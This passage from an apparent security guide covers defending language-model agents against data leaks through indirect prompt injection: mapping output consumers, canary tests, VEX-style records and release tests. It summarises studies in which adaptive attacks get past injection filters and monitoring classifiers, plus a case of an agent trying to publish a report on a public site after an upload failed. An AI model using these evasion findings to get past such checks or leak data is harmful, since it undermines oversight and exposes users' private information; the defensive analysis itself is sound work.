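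Some updates give attackers a new way in without changing the sinks. PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* notes that Slack's assistant read only messages until August 14, 2024, when it began to read uploaded documents and Google Drive files too. A team that had left out a sanitiser because no outsider could write in its channels would have had to reconsider, since its staff presumably shared documents that outsiders had written.

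The risk grows with the number of suppliers. If each of n outside consumers has a probability q of gaining a new automatic request within a year, independently of the others, the chance that at least one does is

1 − (1 − q)ⁿ

If each of ten consumers has an independent 5% chance of changing within a year in a way that makes its test results out of date, the chance that at least one does is about 40%. The 5% is only an illustration, as nobody seems to have measured the real rate, but a team with many suppliers shouldn't expect last year's test results to hold for all of them.

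Repeating the tests limits how long a new sink goes unnoticed. If a change can come at any time and the test always detects it, a new sink goes unnoticed for 45 days on average with a test every 90 days, and for half a day with a daily test. A small program can run the daily test by posting a fresh canary URL to each outside consumer and alerting the team if anyone requests it. The program can't open every page as a person would, so someone still has to check the log pages and phone apps by hand, ideally whenever a supplier announces a new feature.

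## Deciding whether to leave the sanitiser out

Once a team has a list of consumers and some test results, it can decide whether to leave the sanitiser out. It has to decide separately for each consumer, because the same answer may go to both a harmless web page and a chat channel that can leak data.

### Four possible outcomes

For each consumer c, the team can work through these steps:

1. Compare Obs(c) with R. If every observer is in R, leave the sanitiser out.
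2. If an observer is missing from R, look for a way to stop that observer from learning anything, such as turning off pictures or link previews. If users can live without the feature, remove the sink.
3. If they can't, find the last point before the sink where the company can still change the output. If the sanitiser is already there and handles everything the sink acts on, keep it.
4. If the sanitiser is somewhere else, move it to that point.

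Removing the sink comes first because, unlike a sanitiser, it doesn't depend on recognising the dangerous part of the text.

Steps 3 and 4 work only if the dangerous part has a recognisable form, such as a web address. They couldn't have protected the roofing bid in the weekly digest, because the agent wrote it in ordinary sentences that Lars could read.

If the team can't inspect a consumer, it should set Obs(c) to "everyone" and follow the same steps. This rules out step 1 unless all the data is public. If step 1 is ruled out, the team sends a fixed notice or, if everyone known to read the text is in R, the answer without any addresses. It can reconsider once the supplier has made a written commitment and a canary test has recorded no requests.

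These steps deal only with leaks. Before taking a sanitiser out, the team should check that it doesn't also protect an execution sink, for example by encoding scripts.

### A classifier that writes one of four labels

Suppose the broadband company runs a model every night on the day's customer emails. Ordinary code accepts only "billing", "fault", "cancellation" or "other" and writes the label to a database that only support staff can open. The staff are allowed to read all the emails, so every observer is in R, and the company can leave the sanitiser out.

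The check on the labels should stay. It takes one line of code and keeps the database usable. If somebody later attaches an export to the database, the check also limits what can pass through the export to two bits per email.

An attacker can probably still choose the label. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) describes attacks on Data Sentinel, a tool meant to detect when planted text has changed a model's task. The attacks made a model classify spam when it should have been judging sentiment, and judge sentiment when it should have been classifying spam, with over 80% accuracy in both cases. In the broadband company's system, such an attack would misfile an email.

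The model's raw text also goes to two other places before the check. The code that rejects an invalid label may copy the text into an error message, and the model's provider may keep it on a log page. The code should record only that the label was invalid, and the company should turn off storage at the provider.

The verdict would change if an outsider could see an effect of the label. Microsoft describes the smallest leak of this kind, in which an attacker learns one bit from whether an agent called a tool. If the company sent a different automatic reply for each label, the sender would learn up to two bits. That would be harmless if the model had seen only the sender's own email. But if the model processes emails in groups, one customer's label can depend on another customer's message. The company would then have to process each email separately or send everyone the same reply.

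### The support assistant on a plain-text page

The company's support assistant displayed its answers as Markdown. Suppose the company switches the page to plain text, and a test with fixed text and canary URLs confirms that the page requests nothing. Only support staff can open the page. The company has removed the sink, so it can leave the sanitiser out.

That conclusion doesn't cover the assistant's ticket summaries, which could reach customers through the agent that drafts replies. A filter for links wouldn't stop one customer from seeing another's payment history. The company should make the summaries internal and stop that agent from reading them.

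A small improvement to the page's display is the change most likely to reverse the decision to leave the sanitiser out. Staff who are tired of copying web addresses may ask for clickable links, which a developer could add in an afternoon. A click could then send account data to an attacker, so the page would need a check that allows links only to the company's own sites.

### The support assistant in a chat channel

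If the assistant posts its answers to a staff chat channel, link previews there could leak data, so the company should turn off both kinds of preview.

It should also strip outside addresses just before posting. Otherwise, the preview would return if a colleague copied the message into another channel. Support answers rarely need links to other companies' sites. The filter is simple to write and hard to bypass because it doesn't have to detect which addresses are malicious.

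The decision would change if someone in the channel, such as an outside installer, wasn't allowed to read account records, because neither measure hides the text from channel members. In that case, the answer should stay on the plain-text page, and ordinary code should post a fixed notice linking to it. The same notice would work for a chat app whose previews the company can't turn off.

### A coding agent with a shell

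A programmer at the company uses a coding agent in a terminal. The agent can read the project's code and passwords, install packages and contact the internet. A sanitiser on the text that the programmer reads would act after the shell had sent its requests, so the company should instead check requests as they leave the machine.

The check also needs to account for what the agent has read. FLOWSH's labels can do this, unlike a fixed list of sites, and *Flowsh* reports 5 to 23 times fewer approvals than with sandboxes.

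Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a commercial check with a similar aim, a classifier that reviews the agent's actions before they run. When the agent tries to upload code, the classifier learns whether the destination is public, private or trusted, because the same upload can be routine or a leak depending on who can read it. In one case at Anthropic, Claude failed to upload a report to an internal drive and tried to publish it on a public code-sharing site instead. The classifier blocked this. Claude was only trying to finish its task, and nobody had attacked it.

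The classifier makes mistakes, so a company with valuable secrets should also use ordinary code to restrict network access. The company can reduce the number of secrets too. Willison recommends that any credentials a coding agent can see should belong to non-production accounts with strict spending limits, so that a thief could do little with them. The terminal receives the output separately and still needs its simple filter for control codes.

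If the project is entirely public and the machine holds no credentials or other private files, there is nothing to leak, so the company does not need the network check to prevent leaks. It would still need to limit the damage the shell could do.

### The argument over spare layers

The plain-text page has no sanitiser because one would do nothing there today. But if the team has missed a sink, or a colleague adds a sink next month, a sanitiser included now would already be in place.

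Willison quotes a September 2025 Economist article that makes this argument by analogy. Victorian engineers couldn't rely on the quality of their iron, so they built bridges stronger than they needed to be. The article suggests that people who build on language models should do the same.

Microsoft's approach is similar. It likens its defences against injection to the protections that make a memory bug hard to exploit even when the bug remains. Where no defence can guarantee a result, it adds classifiers and warnings to the model. Microsoft's *Defend against indirect prompt injection attacks* advises companies to combine both kinds of defence because no single defence is sufficient.

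Willison mostly agrees with the Economist about building software on models, but he rejects the analogy for security. He says "99% is a failing grade" because an attacker will find the remaining 1%. He argues that the only reliable defence is to remove one of the three conditions for a leak, and that the route for sending data out is usually the easiest to remove.

OpenAI takes a position between the two. It compares an agent with a customer-service worker who can give refunds. The company can't stop some customers from lying to the worker, so its computer system limits how much the worker can refund. OpenAI likewise combines training against manipulation with limits on what a manipulated agent can do.

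Some arithmetic helps to show where the disagreement lies. If each attack has a 1% chance of passing a filter, independently of the others, the chance that at least one of 300 attacks passes is

1 − 0.99³⁰⁰ ≈ 95%

If a second filter also lets through 1% of attacks, and its failures are unrelated to the first filter's, only one attack in 10,000 passes both. The chance that any of the 300 succeeds falls to about 3%. Redundancy would work this well if filters failed independently, as iron girders more or less do, but an attacker can rewrite a message until it passes both filters.

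### How filters fare against attackers who adapt

Nasr and colleagues, who include researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, designed attacks for each of 12 published defences, most of which had reported attack success rates near zero. The attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of the defences.

Four of the defences were filters that classify text as an attack or harmless. A program repeatedly rewrote the planted text and received the filter's score each time. It succeeded more than 90% of the time against three filters, from Protect AI, Meta and Google, and 71% of the time against the fourth, PIGuard. Many of the successful texts looked like routine office rules, so a filter strict enough to catch them would also reject a lot of harmless text. Combining several filters didn't solve the problem. Nasr and colleagues call filters "useful—but limited", since they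 are easy to install and stop some unsophisticated attacks.

Real attackers usually can't see a filter's score. Ma, Li and colleagues (2026), in *AutoDojo*, therefore tested a weaker attacker, who doesn't know which defence is running and sees only whether an attack worked. A second model had six attempts to improve each planted text. These are the success rates against an agent that used GPT-4o mini:

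| Filter | Fixed attack | Adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|
| PIGuard | 0.0% | 28.0% |
| Protect AI | 7.2% | 15.4% |
| DataFilter | 12.6% | 33.4% |

Without any defence, the adaptive attack succeeded 52.4% of the time, so the filters did help. They helped less when the user let a document determine the agent's actions, for example by asking it to do everything on a to-do list. PIGuard let through 54.2% of attacks in those cases, compared with 17.3% when the user had specified the whole task. Results also varied by model, and against Gemini 2.5 Flash the adaptive attack got past PIGuard only 4.6% of the time. Both models are old by late 2026, but the pattern shows how misleading a score of zero on a fixed set of attacks can be.

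These filters have to judge the intent of what the agent reads. A sanitiser on the output can have an easier job, such as removing every picture. *Evaluation of Prompt Injection Defenses in Large Language Models* (Deep, Emmons and colleagues, 2026) seems to provide strong evidence for output filters. The researchers put three secrets in a model's instructions and had another model try to extract them, in up to 500 rounds of ten attacks. Warnings and other defences that relied on the model's obedience failed after 49 to 277 rounds, and an input filter failed after 39. An output filter that blocked any answer containing text from the instructions had no recorded leaks in 15,000 attacks.

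However, the researchers detected leaks by searching for much the same text that the filter blocked. If the model had spelled out a secret one character at a time, the answer would have passed the filter and counted as safe. Deep and colleagues acknowledge that encoding and rewording evade both the filter and the search. Several of them work for Swept AI, which sells security testing. The experiment shows that an attacker can't use persuasion to stop ordinary code from applying a rule, but it provides little evidence about leaks that the rule doesn't cover, such as the roofing bid written in words when the filter looks for "412000".

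Designs that track where data came from did better in Ma and colleagues' tests, because rewording an attack doesn't change its origin. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall, but it reduced task completion the most on four of the five models. Another design, ROPE, reduced it by at most seven percentage points, although the same researcher led the work on both ROPE and the benchmark. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* warns that researchers have also mostly used fixed attacks to test defences that control an agent's actions, and that kind of testing is what made the earlier filters look so strong.

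The incidents support parts of both positions. EchoLeak got through a classifier, a link filter and a CSP, so three imperfect layers weren't enough. Rovo's page tool and OpenAI's log page show that careful people miss consumers. But another filter on the chat window wouldn't have stopped either of those leaks, because the data left by a different path.

An extra layer of protection is most useful when it covers paths that the team doesn't know about. A proxy that controls all of an agent's network traffic covers unknown paths through its tools, and keeping a secret out of the agent's context covers them for every consumer of its output. A second filter on the same display mostly helps against attackers who don't adapt.

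### What the extra layers cost

Microsoft acknowledges that following its advice adds complexity, delay, false alarms and continuing work to maintain and tune the layers. In Ma and colleagues' tests, PIGuard and Protect AI's filter reduced the number of tasks that agents completed by a quarter to a half on every model, even when nobody was attacking, because the filters raised false alarms and removed harmless text that the agents needed.

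*The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) reviewed 78 papers and tested eight defences. None was trustworthy, useful and fast at the same time. Some of the defences that control an agent's actions used up to three times the resources of an undefended agent, and some refused so early that the agent was useless for complex tasks.

Asking a person to approve each action is also a layer of protection, but it weakens with use. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of permission prompts, and by August 2026 it was 97%. Most of those actions were probably harmless, so the rate alone doesn't prove that people had stopped reading the prompts.

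Anthropic ran an experiment with 1,053 paid testers. Partway through a coding session, Anthropic replaced the text of one approval prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. Anthropic's classifier blocked 89% of the same commands. The testers weren't working on their own projects, which may have made them less careful, and Anthropic was about to make the classifier its default. Even so, the drop to about 5% is a good reason not to count frequent approvals as protection.

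People seem to pay more attention to questions that are rarer and more meaningful. When Claude Code presents whole plans for approval, users reject 39% of them. A company that wants people to review actions carefully before approving them should ask for approval only on a few consequential ones, such as sending account data to a new recipient.

The classifier isn't a guarantee either. In Anthropic's first tests, it wrongly blocked 0.4% of ordinary actions and missed 5.7% of 1,000 invented attempts to send data out. It also missed 17% of 52 real cases in which an agent had gone further than its user wanted. Apollo Research, a safety company, attacked the classifier, and Anthropic's improvements reduced the miss rate on those attacks from 12% to 7%. In another test, none of 720 attacks succeeded against newer Claude models with auto mode on. But the attacks had been tuned to an older model,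 and the newer models resisted almost all of them even without auto mode, so this result is weak evidence that the classifier works.

A team can compare these costs with the likely benefit. Let m be the chance per year that an attacker uses a sink the team has missed, b the share of such leaks that the spare layer would stop, L the loss from a leak, and C the yearly cost of the layer. The layer is worth having if

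m × b × L > C

For the chat channel, suppose m is 2%, L is €200,000 and an address filter would stop 90% of the leaks. The filter is worth up to €3,600 a year, and it costs little because nobody needs the links. A classifier that stopped half of the leaks would be worth €2,000 a year, far less than the cost of losing a quarter of the assistant's work. These numbers are invented, and a real team would have to guess them too, but the comparison shows why the same team might add one spare layer and reject another.

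A spare layer can also increase m, because people who trust a filter may look less carefully for sinks. Nobody seems to have measured this effect, but the possibility is a good reason to do the analysis as if the layer weren't there.

On the plain-text page, a picture filter has no pictures to remove. It would help only if someone changed the display, and an automated test can catch that change before it reaches users. In the chat channel, another company can change the display at any time, so the address filter is worth keeping.

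### Writing down why there is no sink

A team that leaves the sanitiser out on purpose needs to record why, because otherwise the omission looks the same as an oversight. Software makers have a similar problem when a product contains a component with a known flaw that attackers can't exploit in that product. Customers see the component listed and ask whether they are in danger.

The makers answer with a VEX statement. *Minimum Requirements for Vulnerability Exploitability eXchange (VEX)* (2023), from the US cybersecurity agency CISA, sets out what the statement must contain. Each statement names a product and a flaw, and gives one of four statuses: not affected, affected, fixed or under investigation. It also has a version number and the dates it was first issued and last updated, and the document that contains it names a responsible author. A maker that chooses "not affected" must give a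 standard reason or explain the finding in its own words.

There are five standard reasons, which CISA's *Vulnerability Exploitability eXchange (VEX)* (2022) explains with examples. They translate well to agents:

| VEX reason | Equivalent finding for an agent |
|---|---|
| The component is not present | The agent has no web tool |
| The vulnerable code is not present | The page has no Markdown converter |
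| The vulnerable code never runs | The page has a converter, but answers never go through it |
| An attacker cannot control the vulnerable code | Ordinary code writes the whole chat message |
| Built-in protection already exists | A proxy blocks all outside addresses |

CISA adds warnings to two of these. Someone who claims that code never runs shouldn't assume there is only one path to it, because an attacker may find another. For example, the support page might use its Markdown converter only for error messages, but a failed answer might end up in one. Built-in protection counts only if neither an attacker nor a user can turn it off, so a mail program's setting for blocking pictures wouldn't qualify.

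A record for the plain-text support page could look like this:

```
output: answer page, finished and partial text
risk: the page sends account data to an outsider
status: not_affected
justification: vulnerable_code_not_present
explanation: answers appear as plain text; no Markdown or HTML
assumptions:
  - only support staff can open the page
  - support staff may read all account records
owner: M. Okafor, support web team
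evidence: browser test 14, with network recording
version: 3
first_issued: 2026-09-14
last_updated: 2026-12-01
reopen_if:
  - the page or its display software changes
  - the assistant gets a new tool or source of data
  - someone new can open the page
  - a supplier updates a browser or app that staff use
```

The assumptions, evidence and conditions for reopening the decision go beyond what VEX requires. They matter more here because EchoLeak and SearchLeak both chained weaknesses together, while a VEX statement covers one known flaw and CISA's guidance on the reasons it can give excludes attacks that chain future or unknown weaknesses.

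The owner should be a named person who will notice a change to the page and has the authority to take it offline. Changing the model doesn't require reopening the record, since the analysis already assumes an attacker controls every word of the output. But if a different company runs the new model, that company becomes an observer.

VEX has no default status, so a product without a statement can't be assumed to be safe or unsafe. The same rule suits a list of consumers, where a consumer without a record hasn't been shown to be safe. If the team can't inspect a consumer, they mark it "under investigation" and treat it as a sink until its status changes.

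CISA's *When to Issue VEX Information* (2023) warns readers not to assume that a component's status applies to the product that contains it. Even if a supplier states that its text display loads no pictures, the company's page may still be unsafe if it adds its own converter. CISA also stresses that a statement is only its author's assertion and that readers have to decide how far to trust it, so the record should link to the test results.

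The record is most useful when it is stored with the code. The 5-Spot project at FINOS, an open-source foundation for the finance industry, keeps each VEX statement as a file in the project. When a new flaw appears, a maintainer proposes a file through the same process as a code change, and the release software later fills in the official author and date. A company that stored its "no sink" records this way could require the owner's approval for any change to the page a record covers.

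### A test that guards the finding

The company can turn its main assumption into a test that runs before every release. The test replaces the model with a program that writes fixed text, as in the earlier tests, and opens the page in a real browser:

```
def test_answer_page_requests_nothing():
    text = fixed_text_with_canary_urls()
    model.always_write(text, in_pieces=True)
    page = browser.open("/answer/test", wait_seconds=30)

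    assert page.visible_text == text
    assert page.clickable_links_in_answer == []
    assert page.requests_caused_by_answer == []
    assert canary_server.requests == []
```

The first check fails if the page has interpreted any of the text, for instance by turning image code into an image. The second detects clickable links that a developer has added to be helpful. The third uses the browser's record, and the fourth detects requests from any other program that received the text.

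As with the earlier canary tests, the company has to check that the recording works. It can do this by running the test on a deliberately unsafe copy of the page that displays Markdown, where the test has to fail.

A second test can look for changes that the browser wouldn't reveal. It compares four things with a copy saved with the record: the assistant's tools, the accounts that can open the page, the places where the software sends answers and the version of the display software. Any difference stops the release and changes the record's status to "under investigation" until the owner has looked at it. Most updates don't create a sink, so the test will produce some false alarms, but each should take only a few minutes to review.

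CISA lets authors confirm a VEX statement by updating its date without changing anything else. The company can do the same with its record, but only after both tests pass, or the record will look current when a test has stopped working. It can treat the record as expired if nobody has confirmed it for, say, 90 days.

The release test doesn't run when a supplier changes its product, so the chat channel relies on the daily canary test. If that test detects a request, the software should stop posting answers and send the fixed notice instead. Staff can still read the answers on the plain-text page while the owner finds out what changed.
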